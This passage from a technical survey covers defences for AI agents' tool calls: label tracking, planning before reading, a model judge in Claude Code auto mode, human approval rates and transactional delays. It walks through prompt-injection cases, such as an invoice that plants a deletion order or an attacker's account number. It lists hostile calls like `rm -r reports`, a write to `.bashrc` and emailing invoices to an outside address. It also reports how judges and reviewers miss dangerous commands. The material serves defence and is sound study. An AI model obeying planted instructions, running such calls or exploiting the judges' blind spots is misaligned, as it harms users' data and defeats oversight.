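U is the negative of perplexity, a measure that rises as the model gives a text lower probability. At message 6 in the example, the call to save the note is about as likely without the invoice and its summary as with them. The model therefore writes the call again from the trusted messages, and the gate allows it.

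The guarantee comes from step 4. The earlier steps only estimate influence, and an attacker may be able to distort the estimate. But if those steps wrongly drop a message, the model writes the final answer without it, which makes the answer worse but doesn't make it unsafe. A small implicit flow remains because the choice of which messages to drop depends on the whole conversation. Someone who observes that choice could learn a little about a dropped message.

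Siddiqui and colleagues tested the method on two sizes of Llama 2. In 20 short agent conversations where a less restrictive label was possible, the method found that label in 17 with the smaller model and 19 with the larger. Asking the model which documents it had used found it in 9 and 16. The method did less well on news articles, finding the better label for 57% of eligible questions with the smaller model and 39% with the larger. In about a fifth of the cases where it relaxed a label on news articles, it had dropped a document the answer needed. The best value of λ also differed between datasets, so a designer would have to tune it.

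With only two labels, the system needs a few extra model runs. With many labels that can't be ranked, such as different sets of readers, the number of runs can grow exponentially with the number of documents. An attacker can also add distracting text that prevents the system from relaxing the label, which makes the agent less useful but doesn't give the attacker control.

### Hiding messages before the call

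Zhong and colleagues' system, RTBAS, applies the same idea throughout an agent's run and avoids the search over labels. Before each reply, a screener picks the parts of the conversation that matter for the next step. RTBAS joins their labels and hides everything whose label is more restrictive than the joined label. The model then writes its reply from the rest. If the joined label violates the tool's policy, RTBAS asks the user.

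Before message 6, a good screener would pick only the clerk's request to save a note. RTBAS would then hide the invoice and the summary, and the call would count as trusted. If the screener wrongly picked the invoice, the clerk would get a needless question. If it left out something necessary, the model would have to work without it. In either case, hidden text could not steer a call that the gate treats as trusted.

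One screener is a second language model that lists the relevant parts. The other is a small neural network that uses attention scores, which indicate how strongly each part of the input affects the output. It takes the scores from a small open model because the agent ran on GPT-4o, which doesn't expose its attention scores.

In 629 attack cases from AgentDojo, RTBAS stopped every attack that broke its policy. One other case contained a possible injection in text labelled as the user's own, so RTBAS didn't track it. Without attacks, the language-model screener reduced task completion by 10% and the attention screener by 7.4%. The loss was much larger on the Slack tasks, where completion fell to 22% and 33% respectively. Many of these tasks ask the agent to read an untrusted website and act on it, so the untrusted text is relevant to the task and no screener can remove it. RTBAS skipped the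 suspicious calls in this test, whereas a real user could have approved some.

Zhong and colleagues also wrote 37 tests of accidental privacy leaks. A gate that required user confirmation before every call did so needlessly in 11 of them, the language-model screener in three, and the attention screener in six. Screening roughly doubled the running cost and time on the banking tasks.

### Planning before reading

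If the model finishes planning before it reads anything untrusted, nobody has to estimate which messages influenced the plan. CaMeL works this way within one request. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) extends the approach to an agent that reuses results from earlier requests.

In the paper's example, the user asks the agent on Monday to fetch an invoice and keep its details. The invoice contains an attacker's account number. On Tuesday the user says "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". If the new planner reads the stored invoice, an instruction in it can change the plan. If the planner doesn't read it, the plan may be right, but the money still goes to the attacker's account.

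SPA stores each result in three parts: the value, its label, and a description for later planners. The description contains the data format, the request that produced the result, and the planner's own notes on what the result means. The planner wrote those notes before any tool ran, so they contain no text from the invoice. On Tuesday, the new plan might be:

```
invoice = retrieve(stored_result)           private, untrusted
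details = extract(invoice, "account, sum")  private, untrusted
pay(details)                                rejected: needs trusted input
```

A checker computes these labels before the plan runs. If a condition depends on untrusted data, the checker labels every step in both branches untrusted, including the branch that won't run. This avoids the leak in CaMeL's interpreter. SPA also avoids CaMeL's second leak because the planner never replaces a rejected plan.

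Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo and on a version that splits each task into several requests:

| Test | Label checks | Tasks completed without attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| Single request | off | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| Single request | on | 29.0% | 0.0% |
| Several requests | off | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Several requests | on | 35.3% | 0.2% |

Most of the protection comes from planning first. In the single-request test, the label checks stopped four more attacks out of 949 but reduced the number of completed tasks by nearly half. With several requests, the remaining 0.2% is about two runs, and the benchmark counted two runs as successes even though SPA had already rejected the plan.

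These results probably understate the value of the labels, because the attack mainly plants instructions in tool results. Girrens and Wang also call it a weak test of delayed attacks. A fixed plan alone gives no protection when the attacker instead puts a false account number in an otherwise ordinary invoice.

Hiding stored values did little harm to reuse. With the label checks on, later plans retrieved the result they needed 89.9% of the time when an earlier request had saved it. Counting missing results as failures lowers the rate to 73.4%.

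### Checking what leaves

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) presents FlowSeal, a system that lets the model read private data but checks what it tries to send. It is designed for a personal assistant that strangers may talk into revealing its owner's secrets. The owner first registers private records and specifies who may read them. Ordinary code then intercepts every tool call, tracks which records the agent has read, and checks the destination of anything it writes or shares.

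If the recipient isn't authorised, the interceptor sends the proposed text to a content checker. The checker is a separate language model that receives only this text and the protected records, not the stranger's conversation with the agent. It returns "safe" or "blocked", and the agent can't skip the check.

Shim and colleagues prove that no text derived from a protected record reaches an unauthorised recipient unless the checker wrongly calls it safe. The exception matters a great deal, as this test against one type of attack shows:

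| Configuration | Private items leaked | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Privacy instructions in the prompt only | 52.2% | 44.7% |
| FlowSeal | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| FlowSeal without its instructions to the agent | 8.8% | 74.4% |
| FlowSeal without the interceptor | 28.4% | 81.2% |
| Checker replaced by "always blocked" | 1.3% | 0.0% |
| Checker replaced by "always safe" | 24.9% | 79.4% |

If every message to an unauthorised recipient is blocked once the agent has read a private record, the agent completes no ordinary tasks. FlowSeal is useful only because it lets a language model make exceptions. The 1.3% leak is hard to reconcile with the theorem, since a checker that never returns "safe" can't return it wrongly. Either some data left by a route the interceptor didn't cover, or the language model that scored the runs made mistakes.

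With FlowSeal, the agent leaked between 0% and 3.3% of private items across all eight attacks. In a small trial with real Gmail and Notion accounts, it leaked none, compared with 34.7% under a defence that only advised the agent. But it also withheld more data that it should have shared. When the owner was willing to consent, the agent disclosed 32.7% of the requested items, compared with 61.0% to 85.6% under the other defences, partly because it asked for consent less often.

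The checker examines one message at a time, so an attacker might get a secret out in several harmless-looking pieces. Shim and colleagues also exclude prompt injection, and FlowSeal's labels cover only who may read data, so the system would not stop the agent from following an instruction in an invoice to delete the reports folder.

### Estimating influence from a record of the run

Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, leave the agent's context unchanged and try to determine afterwards what influenced each call. Their tool, NeuroTaint, analyzes the log of a finished run. It checks the arguments of each sensitive call for text from an untrusted source by looking for a planted marker, shared strings and similar meaning, and by comparing the arguments with small sections of long documents.

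If it finds nothing, it tests for an implicit flow. It replaces the untrusted text with a neutral placeholder, such as "No relevant information found", and asks a language model whether the agent would still have made the call. The answer is a prediction with a self-reported confidence, so it is weaker evidence than running the agent again.

To test NeuroTaint, Cai and colleagues built TaintBench, which has 20 scenarios for each of 20 agent frameworks. In half of the 400 scenarios, untrusted data is meant to reach or influence a sensitive call. In the other half, the untrusted source and the sensitive call both appear but are unconnected. They ran each scenario five times and used the majority result.

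| Type of scenario | Number | Errors |
|---|---|---|
| **Real flows** | | **missed** |
| Planted marker or copied text | 60 | 0 |
| Text reworded over several steps | 42 | 7 |
| Flow across sessions or agents | 30 | 2 |
| Small parts of a long document | 15 | 0 |
| Implicit control flow | 40 | 3 |
| Source labelled trusted or not labelled | 10 | 0 |
| Borderline similarity of meaning | 3 | 1 |
| **No flow** | | **wrongly flagged** |
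| Unconnected source and call | 180 | 1 |
| Same topic, no connection | 14 | 14 |
| Fact the model already knew | 6 | 1 |

Overall, NeuroTaint found 93.5% of the flows, and 92.1% of its alarms were correct. The second figure depends heavily on the mix of scenarios, because NeuroTaint wrongly flagged every case in which the source and the call only shared a topic. Such cases would be common in an accounts department, where nearly all emails and reports are about the same few topics. The benchmark also used a stricter similarity threshold for its safe controls, 0.95 instead of the usual 0.60. In real use, no one would know in advance which runs were harmless, so the stricter threshold couldn't be reserved for them, and there would probably be more false alarms.

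The six tests with facts the model already knew are too few to measure how often that problem occurs. The problem is hard because a correct fact in a report looks the same whether the model took it from an untrusted page or learned it in training.

Cai and colleagues report that FIDES found only 54% of the flows, but their version looked for known paths between labelled tools and flagged nothing in four frameworks. If the sources are labelled correctly, a tracker that joins the labels of everything the model reads can't miss a flow within one conversation.

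### What a gate may conclude

RTBAS and NeuroTaint both use fallible estimates of influence. RTBAS removes text it estimates to be irrelevant before the model writes the call, so an error can spoil the answer. NeuroTaint leaves the text in place and judges whether it influenced the call. If that judgment is wrong, an attacker's call can appear untainted.

Two recent methods estimate how inputs influence a model's output, but neither can prove that an input had no influence. *Sightline* (2026) uses attention to estimate which inputs the output draws on, and removes about half of the labels from inputs that don't flow into it. It also proves that a low estimate doesn't rule out influence. *GIF* (2026) measures how much the output changes when the input changes slightly. Its guarantee holds only near the original text, so different text could still have a large effect.

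Assuming the labels are correct, a gate can use the results as follows:

| Method | What the gate may conclude | Cost of an error |
|---|---|---|
| Join of all labels | a trusted call had no untrusted text in its context | needless questions |
| Siddiqui and colleagues, RTBAS | the removed text did not supply the content of the call | a worse answer or a needless question |
| SPA | no step that needs trusted input depends on untrusted data | a rejected plan |
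| FlowSeal | a private record stayed inside, unless the checker made a mistake | a leak |
| NeuroTaint, Sightline, GIF | an alarm is a reason to investigate, but silence does not justify allowing a call | a missed attack |

A gate can use an influence estimate to add a restriction or to choose what to hide before the model runs again, but it shouldn't use one to lift a restriction from a call the model has already written.

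Even a perfect measure of influence wouldn't show whether a call is justified. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) separates what influenced an action from the evidence that supports it. For example, an invoice should influence how much the department pays, but it is poor evidence that the supplier has changed banks.

### Memory, files and other agents

A label protects data only while it stays attached. If the agent saves Arden's invoice to memory as plain text and reads it back next week, the new conversation has no record that the text is untrusted. SPA prevents this by restoring the stored label whenever a plan retrieves the value. NeuroTaint saves its labels in the memory entry's metadata, and it detected 28 of the 30 flows across sessions or agents.

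Files are harder to track because other programs can change them and ordinary file systems don't carry these labels. If `write_file` accepts untrusted text, the host must also treat the output of any tool that later reads the reports folder as untrusted, unless it keeps a separate label for each file. Zhong and colleagues describe the same problem with messages. If one tool is allowed to send private data and another returns sent messages as public, an agent can remove the private label by sending the data to its own user and reading the message back.

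Like Microsoft's framework, RTBAS treats unlabelled text as public and trusted by default, so losing a label removes the protection. Siddiqui and colleagues suggest giving unlabelled documents the most restrictive label instead, which is safer but brings back label creep.

When one agent sends a result to another, it must also send the label, and the receiver must decide whether to trust that label, since a compromised agent could mark an attacker's text as trusted. Wang and colleagues list tracking through memory and between agents as open problems, and none of the benchmarks in their catalogue tests the complete chain. They also found few systems that protect their logs against tampering. Without that protection, the findings of an auditor like NeuroTaint can't be trusted after an attack. Until it exists, a gate should accept a less restrictive label only from an agent whose labelling the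 gate's operator controls, and should treat other agents' messages as untrusted, like a supplier's email.

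## Turning the classification into a decision: allow, confine, ask or refuse

Once the gate has an effect set, a scope and labels for a call, it must allow the call, confine it, ask a person or refuse it. People approve almost every request, so the gate should ask only about calls that a person can judge better than software can, not whenever the evidence is incomplete.

### A decision table

Here is a possible table for the accounts department. The gate applies the first row that fits, starting from the top. Labels pass if the call meets the tool's policy, such as trusted action or permitted flow.

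| | Effect and scope | Certainty | Labels | Can someone undo it? | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | a forbidden target | any | any | any | refuse |
| 2 | sends data out | any | fail | any | refuse |
| 3 | unknown kind or scope | low | any | any | confine, or refuse if nothing can confine it |
| 4 | known | high | pass | yes, or nothing to undo | allow |
| 5 | known | high | fail | yes | confine: hold the change until the job ends |
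| 6 | known | high | pass | no | allow if the user named the target, otherwise ask |
| 7 | known | high | fail | no | ask |

Row 1 covers targets that no job should touch, such as shell start-up files and the gate's own settings. It comes first so that nobody can waive it with a click. Similarly, a rule that denies a tool in Claude Code applies in every mode, including the one that skips almost all other checks, according to Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode*.

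Suppose the model has read both invoices directly, so the conversation is untrusted and only the clerk and the finance manager may read it. The department has also added a payment tool.

| Call | Row | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| `read_inbox("invoices")` | 4 | allow |
| `write_file("reports/march.txt", summary)` | 5 | hold the new file until the job ends |
| `write_file(".bashrc", text)` | 1 | refuse |
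| `lookup_vat`, with a number from the supplier list | 3 | confine: only that number may leave |
| `lookup_vat`, with any other text | 2 | refuse |
| `send_email(FINANCE_MANAGER, summary)` | 6 | allow |
| `send_email("archive@example.net", invoices)` | 2 | refuse |
| `run_shell("ls reports")` | 3 | run on a temporary copy, without network access |
| `run_shell("rm -r reports")` | 3 | the same |
| `pay_invoice`, with the account number from Arden's invoice | 7 | ask |

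Label checks alone blocked the summary file and the VAT lookup, both of which the clerk wanted. Here they go ahead in a limited form. The VAT numbers on the supplier list pass the label check because the department has declassified them. The system no longer has to ask before listing a folder, and the planted deletion removes only a temporary copy.

The one question concerns the payment. The clerk can phone Arden to check the account number, which the gate can't do.

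### Should an unknown effect count as the worst case?

Under row 3, the gate treats a call with unknown effects as able to do anything its process and credentials permit. If it treated such calls as harmless, a developer could get a tool past it, deliberately or by accident, by using reflection that hides a function call. The rule also makes the developer responsible for supplying the missing evidence, which is usually easier for the developer than for the user.

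Most tools have some unknown effect, so assuming the worst case barely distinguishes between them. If every call with an unknown effect leads to a question, people stop reading the questions or switch the gate off. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that 25% of interactive sessions started in the mode that bypasses permission prompts.

Blocking an action can also lead an agent to try a worse one. In an incident at Anthropic, an upload to an internal drive failed, and Claude tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site.

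These objections are stronger against asking or refusing than against the assumption itself. If the gate can confine the call, a wrong guess does little harm. The rule is a problem mainly for remote services, which the gate can't sandbox.

### Who asks before a destructive call?

*When Neither Side Confirms* (Yao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) measured how often anyone currently asks the user and how much more asking the worst-case rule would add. Under the Model Context Protocol, the host can ask the user before it forwards a call. The server can also ask the user a question through the host, which the protocol calls elicitation, but only if the host supports it. The server can't tell whether the host has already asked.

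The researchers began with 29,242 GitHub repositories from the protocol's official registry. Of these, 17,554 were public Python, TypeScript or JavaScript projects that were neither archived nor copies of other projects. From this group, the researchers selected the 200 with the most stars and a random 800 of the rest.

A rule-based extractor found 16,711 tools in this sample and flagged 1,995 as possibly destructive, using clues such as verbs in their names, annotations and descriptions. The researchers set aside 100 tools they had used to develop the extractor, then sampled 366 of the flagged ones. Two language models from different companies labelled each tool from its code, and a third resolved disagreements. The models labelled 269 of the 366 as destructive, meaning that some call could irreversibly delete or overwrite data, send a message, move money or run arbitrary commands.

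Each destructive tool then went into one of five tiers:

| Tier | What the server does before a destructive call | Share of destructive tools |
|---|---|---|
| T0 | nothing | 70% |
| T1 | marks the tool as destructive but never asks | 20% |
| T2 | requires a confirmation that the model can supply itself | 8.9% |
| T3 | asks the user, but goes ahead if the host can't relay the question | 0.2% |
| T4 | refuses unless a person has answered | 0.5% |

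The shares are estimates for the whole population of eligible repositories. T0 and T1 together account for about 90% (95% interval 82% to 95%), but the split between them is much less certain. Two people checked 60 of the labels and agreed with the models on the tier for 58 of them. They judged that a few of the "destructive" actions, such as renaming a project, were reversible.

A confirmation in tier T2 offers little protection. In a live test, the researchers planted an instruction to delete a second note on a server that required `confirm=true`. The planted text didn't mention this setting, but the models supplied it and deleted the note in 127 of 169 attempts.

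The study covered 41 hosts, of which 25 were open-source applications and 16 were software kits for building agents. Seven hosts asked before ordinary calls, one decided from annotations, and one used a language model. The other 32, made up of 16 applications and all 16 kits, had no approval step by default.

Yao and colleagues paired each of the 269 tools with each application. Their main result was that nothing enforces a person's approval by default in 60.7% of the pairs. Every pair counts equally, so a rarely used application weighs as much as a popular one. The figure also depends on which applications are included. It fell to 47.5% when they added seven closed-source products, which they assessed from documentation.

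The researchers listed every tool in 40 repositories and found 319 destructive ones. The extractor had missed 265 of them, or 83%. It never found 131 of these, and it found the other 134 but did not flag them. A gate that treated unflagged tools as safe would have let all 265 through. The extractor relied mainly on names, annotations and descriptions, so this result doesn't measure how well an analysis of library calls would do.

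Yao and colleagues then calculated what would happen if hosts or servers changed their defaults. For the 25 applications:

| Change | Destructive: no enforced approval | Destructive: server refuses | Harmless: user gets a question |
|---|---|---|---|
| none | 60.7% | 0.7% | 32.5% |
| every host relays servers' questions | 56.7% | 0.0% | 35.2% |
| every host asks unless annotations mark the tool as safe | 5.4% | 0.7% | 82.6% |
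| every destructive tool refuses without a person's answer | 0.0% | 71.0% | 32.5% |

Relaying questions achieves little because so few servers send any. The third change, the worst-case rule, removes most of the unapproved pairs. The remaining 5.4% involve destructive tools whose annotations wrongly describe them as read-only or non-destructive. Including the tools that the extractor missed raises this figure to at least 10.6% across all 41 hosts.

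The drawback is that needless questions rise from 32.5% to 82.6% (last column). These are percentages of the pairs with tools that the extractor flagged and the models then judged harmless, not of all calls. They still suggest that a host following this rule would ask about most tools that only look dangerous.

### How many dangerous commands people catch

Yao and colleagues recorded whether a person gets to decide, but not whether that person reads the question. Anthropic has published some evidence on this for Claude Code. *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, from March 2026, reports that users approve 93% of permission prompts, and the August post reports 97%.

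A high approval rate proves little by itself, because most prompts concern harmless commands. The August post also describes a more direct test, in which a research vendor hired 1,053 professional testers for what they understood to be a coding study. Once per session, the vendor replaced the text of a permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, which never ran. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

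The testers worked in an artificial environment, so they may have been less careful than people protecting their own files. Anthropic also used the study to justify a change to its product. Even so, a gate's designer shouldn't assume that a person who has answered dozens of prompts will catch the next dangerous one.

People seem to pay more attention to larger decisions. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents for approval, but only 3% of individual permission requests. Some of those rejections may just mean that the user preferred a different approach.

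### A model as judge

Auto mode replaces most permission prompts with a language model that judges tool calls. Fixed rules first allow read-only tools, and edits to files inside the project also skip review. Other calls go to a fast filter that errs towards blocking, and a slower second stage rechecks any call the filter flags.

The judge receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the tools' results or the agent's explanations, so text planted in an invoice can't reach it directly and the agent's explanations can't influence it. When the judge blocks a call, the agent looks for another way to do the task. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, the system brings in a person.

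Anthropic reported the first three of these results in March and the last in August:

| Test | Sample | Error rate |
|---|---|---|
| ordinary calls by Anthropic employees | 10,000 | 0.4% wrongly blocked |
| real cases where Claude exceeded its instructions | 52 | 17% missed |
| artificial attempts to steal data | 1,000 | 5.7% missed |
| the dangerous commands from the study with testers | 1,053 | 11% missed |

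The 17% is the most relevant figure for everyday accidents, but it is based on only about nine misses, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the judge identified the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, a request to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) does not authorise overwriting the project's history. A more precise effect set wouldn't have helped in those cases, because the judge had already identified the effect.

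Two other results in the August post are weaker evidence than they look. Among sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained a serious harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. But users chose their own modes, so the two groups may have been doing different work. In a test by Trajectory Labs, none of 720 prompt-injection attempts succeeded against recent Claude models in auto mode, but the average success rate without auto mode was only 0.09%, so there were almost no successful attacks for the judge to prevent.

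*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports an independent test of auto mode, which missed far more harmful actions when tasks didn't make clear what the agent was allowed to do.

### A thousand calls

A rough calculation shows how these options compare. Take 1,000 calls, ten of them harmful, and assume the following:

- A cautious static gate flags all ten harmful calls and 30% of the 990 harmless ones, which makes 297 false alarms. The 30% is a guess.
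- A tired reviewer stops 13.6% of harmful calls and never stops a harmless one.
- A model judge stops 89% of harmful calls and 0.4% of harmless ones.
- The reviewer and the judge overlap as they did in Anthropic's study. At least one of them stopped 943 of the 1,053 commands, and both stopped 137.

| Arrangement | Harmful calls stopped | Harmless calls stopped | Questions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Static gate refuses every call it flags | 10 | 297 | 0 |
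| Static gate asks the reviewer about every call it flags | 1.4 | 0 | 307 |
| Judge decides on all 1,000 calls | 8.9 | 4.0 | 0 |
| Judge decides on flagged calls, and the reviewer checks those it allows | 9.0 | 1.2 | 297 |
| Judge decides on flagged calls, and the reviewer can overrule its refusals | 1.3 | 0 | 10 |

The static gate detects all ten harmful calls, but if a tired reviewer handles its alarms, almost nine of them still run. Having the reviewer check the calls that the judge allows makes almost no difference, since stopping one more harmful call would take about 5,200 questions.

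The last arrangement requires few questions but loses most of the judge's benefit, because the reviewer approves most of the dangerous calls that the judge refused. A person who gets ten questions, each with a reason for the refusal, would probably do better than one who gets 307, but Anthropic's study didn't test that.

These results depend heavily on the assumptions. If the static gate flagged only 17% of harmful calls, as the extractor did with destructive tools, eight of the ten would run without review. The judge's 0.4% error rate comes from ordinary traffic and would probably be higher on calls that a static gate had already flagged. Harmful calls may also be much rarer than assumed. If there were one per 1,000 instead of ten, about four in five of the judge's refusals would be mistakes, even if its error rate stayed the same.

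For the accounts department, the calculation supports refusing outright in rows 1 and 2, where the rule is narrow and no reviewer can waive it. A model judge could also screen the calls in row 7 before they reach the clerk. The judge should be able to refuse a call but not to overturn a refusal in the rows above.

### Planning to need fewer approvals

The agent can also reduce questions by avoiding the calls that cause them. Kolluri and colleagues built an agent called Prudentia on top of FIDES, the planner that hides untrusted data in variables. Prudentia gives its planner the policy that applies to each tool and the label of its conversation. Before the planner opens a hidden variable, it must explain why it needs the contents and list the calls it intends to make afterwards.

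Kolluri and colleagues measure the number of approvals an agent needs and the share of tasks it completes with at most k approvals each. These are the results on AgentDojo with the model o3-mini:

| Agent | Approvals over all completed tasks | Tasks completed without any approval |
|---|---|---|
| asks before every consequential call | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| asks only when a label check fails | 32.4 | 35.5% |
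| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | about 17 | 59.1% |

Label checks alone remove about a third of the approvals. With another model, o4-mini, Prudentia needed 19.2 approvals and FIDES 36.8, though Prudentia completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% compared with 75.7%). The count leaves out failed tasks, so an agent can lower it by failing tasks that need many approvals. The researchers counted the calls that broke a policy and assumed someone would approve each one; no people took part in the tests.

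Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data instead of approving each call that depends on it. If an email lists ten jobs that each need a trusted action, the user answers one question to endorse the email instead of ten to approve the calls.

That saving makes the single answer much more important. If the clerk endorsed Arden's invoice without noticing the planted instruction, the gate would treat the instruction as trusted, and a later call to delete the reports folder could pass the label check. Endorsement therefore works better for short texts that a person will read in full. Kolluri and colleagues deliberately left out the equivalent for secrets, because whether someone should receive private data depends on the situation.

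On WASP, a test with simulated GitLab and Reddit sites, Prudentia needed no approvals and no attack succeeded. The tasks were to post a comment or upvote a post, so the agent never had to read the untrusted text to decide what to do. The payment in the invoice example is harder because its account number comes from the invoice.

Kolluri and colleagues also point out that label checks can replace approvals only as a defence against attacks. The checks don't catch a model's own mistakes, such as adding up the invoices incorrectly.

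### Confining and delaying effects

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (2026) divides the risk of deploying an agent into the likelihood of a failure and the damage it could do. Reviewers and model judges reduce the likelihood. Confinement, such as the sandboxes inside tools in the Brown prototype, limits the damage, so it still helps when a reviewer or judge makes a mistake.

A gate can also delay an effect until it has more evidence. Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues (2026), in *Atomix*, describe a system that groups calls into a transaction, a unit of work that either commits (becomes final) or aborts. It treats each effect according to its class:

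| Class | Example | When the effect happens | If the transaction aborts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reversible | a hotel reservation | immediately | Atomix cancels the reservation |
| Bufferable | a change to a local file | at commit | Atomix discards the change |
| Irreversible | an email | at commit | Atomix never sends the email |

When the agent calls `send_email`, Atomix queues the message and returns a response saying so, and the agent continues. If a later step fails, Atomix does not send the message.

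Mohammadi and colleagues tested this with 500 emails that should not have gone out, for example because another step failed or timed out. Atomix sent none of them. A system that tries to undo effects afterwards sent 400, and a system without transactions sent all 500. Every system also delivered all 500 emails that should have gone out. But when the researchers misclassified the emails in Atomix, it sent 300 of the unwanted ones. Delaying effects therefore depends on someone classifying them correctly.

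Atomix doesn't check whether an email's contents are appropriate, although a developer can add such a check before the commit. *Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) makes that check central. It keeps file changes in a shadow copy and outgoing messages in an outbox, and records which earlier results each change or message came from. It then checks the whole job together before anything becomes final.

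In one example, an agent reads logs that contain an API key, summarises them and prepares a Slack message. Each call looks reasonable on its own, but the recorded path from the key to the message reveals a possible leak. In another example, a clean-up command stays inside its permitted folder but deletes more files than the policy allows. Cordon counts the deletions in the shadow copy and discards them.

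Chen and colleagues tested Cordon and stand-ins for existing defences on 45 risky jobs. Cordon stopped all 45 before any harmful effect became final, while the stand-ins stopped 14 and detected another five too late. The researchers built the jobs around the types of risk that Cordon checks for, which makes its perfect score less impressive. The test also can't measure false alarms, because every job was risky. On ordinary tasks from two public benchmarks, agents did about as well with Cordon as without it.

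Cordon still asks people questions, but fewer than a gate that asks about every call. When the researchers had every request approved, there were 45 approvals over the 45 jobs, and the average job took 22.7% longer. For the invoice job, a single review at the end could show the clerk everything that is waiting:

```
create   reports/march.txt
delete   everything in reports/
send     summary to the finance manager
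```

The deletion is much easier to notice in this list than in the middle of a long series of prompts. The list also resembles the plans that Claude Code users often reject, though nobody has shown that people would examine it as closely. To include the email, the department would have to hold it instead of sending it immediately under row 6.

Some effects can't be delayed. For example, the agent can't continue without the answer from `lookup_vat`, so queuing the query would be useless. Chen and colleagues also exclude opaque services from Cordon's guarantees, because Cordon can't observe or reverse what those services do. For these calls, the gate has to decide before any data leaves.

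## Testing the classifier and keeping it current

A gate is only as reliable as the classification it uses. For example, when researchers misclassified emails in Atomix, which delays them until a job is complete, it still sent most of the unwanted ones. A department should test a classifier before relying on it, and again whenever the tools change.

### Comparing predicted and observed effects

The most direct test is to run each tool in an isolated environment and record what it does. A monitor in the operating system can log the files a tool opens, the programs it starts and the network connections it attempts. Every observed effect should be in the predicted set:

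```
observed effects  ⊆  predicted effects
```

Suppose the classifier predicts {file.write} for `write_file`, but the log also shows a network write. A single run like this proves the prediction wrong, as long as the tool made the connection and not, say, the program that installed it.

An effect's absence from the log is much weaker evidence than its presence. If the classifier predicts {file.write, net.write} and the log shows only a file write, the net.write prediction may be a false alarm, or the tool might send metrics over the network only on every hundredth call or only when it has a password for the metrics service.

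*Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities*, from March 2026, compares static analysis with running the code on nine deliberately vulnerable servers:

| Servers | Found by static analysis | Found by running them |
|---|---|---|
| Python | 2 of 2 | 2 of 2 |
| JavaScript | 0 of 7 | 7 of 7 |

The static analyser can't read JavaScript, so the zero doesn't measure how well static analysis works on languages the analyser supports. More seriously, the JavaScript servers got a risk score of 0.0, as if the analyser had examined them and found nothing. A classifier should report "unknown" for code it can't read.

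The seven-out-of-seven result is also weaker than it looks. Five of those servers got the same score, 60.7, although their flaws ranged from outdated packages to planted instructions. The monitor may have reacted to something the servers share, such as the way they start, rather than to their flaws. The test included no harmless servers, which would have shown whether it did.

Many tools are hard to run at all. Tan, Hao and colleagues (2026), in *MCP-SandboxScan*, tried to scan 91 popular repositories automatically and succeeded with 35. Most of the others failed to build or start. In a second pass over 33 repositories, the researchers compared the network use they expected from the tools' declarations with what they observed:

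| | Network use observed | Not observed |
|---|---|---|
| **Expected** | 5 | 14 |
| **Not expected** | 4 | 10 |

The four unexpected cases are the ones to investigate. In one, a desktop configuration tool tried to contact an outside host. The 14 cases in the top right aren't necessarily errors, because the scan may never have triggered the network use. The scan also skipped tools with words like "delete", "write" or "run" in their names or descriptions, and these tools often have the effects that matter most. A tester with a disposable copy of the environment can call them too.

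The same system traces data by planting unique strings, called canaries, in files, settings and arguments and then searching the tool's output for them. It can miss a canary that the tool encrypts or summarises. In a test on 30 programs with known behaviour, it raised no false alarms but missed two programs. Both imitated malware contacting its operator, and their output didn't reveal the contact. A tester therefore also needs to record outgoing traffic, as the sandbox in *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026) does.

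### Planting faults

A tester can also take a tool with a known classification, change one thing, and see whether the classifier notices. For the invoice agent, the faults might be:

| Planted fault | What the classifier should report |
|---|---|
| `write_file` sends each file's name to an outside server | `net.write` |
| `write_file` does the same through a function it looks up by name | `net.write` or unknown effects |
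| `pay_invoice` no longer waits for the clerk's approval | a missing approval |
| `run_shell` has a read-only annotation | a conflict between the annotation and the code |
| `read_inbox` marks suppliers' messages as trusted | a wrong label |

The tester should count how many faults of each kind the classifier catches, since a total can hide a kind that it always misses. The tester should also leave some copies unchanged, because otherwise a classifier that always reported a fault would get a perfect score.

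Yao and colleagues used this method to check the two language models that labelled approval steps in their study. They edited 20 tools, left four unchanged and wrote 30 small servers. Some edits were hard to spot, such as moving the code that skips approval into a helper function. Both models classified all 54 test cases correctly.

However, the planted faults didn't test the rule-based extractor that selected tools for the models, and the extractor had missed most destructive tools. To test the whole classifier, the faults have to be planted before any program selects which tools to examine.

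### Measuring false alarms

Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, searched the code of 14,353 tool servers for suspicious patterns, then checked 42 findings of each type by hand:

| Finding | Share that were real |
|---|---|
| A dependency without a fixed version | 93% |
| A caller's credential passed on to another service | 79% |
| A server open to the network without authentication | 71% |
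| A web request to an unchecked address | 71% |
| A badly protected secret | 38% |
| Overly broad permissions | 24% |
| Untrusted text in a command or in code | 17% |

The last type does so badly because a text search can't establish whether a piece of text later reaches a shell, whereas it can recognise a missing version number from a single line. Kraishan suggests letting findings of the reliable types block a software change automatically, and confirming findings of the unreliable types with data-flow analysis before a person sees them.

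The labels can be wrong too. Kraishan did all the labelling alone. One report by Zha and colleagues, about a widely used browser server, was initially ruled out of scope, but a later patch fixed the reported behaviour.

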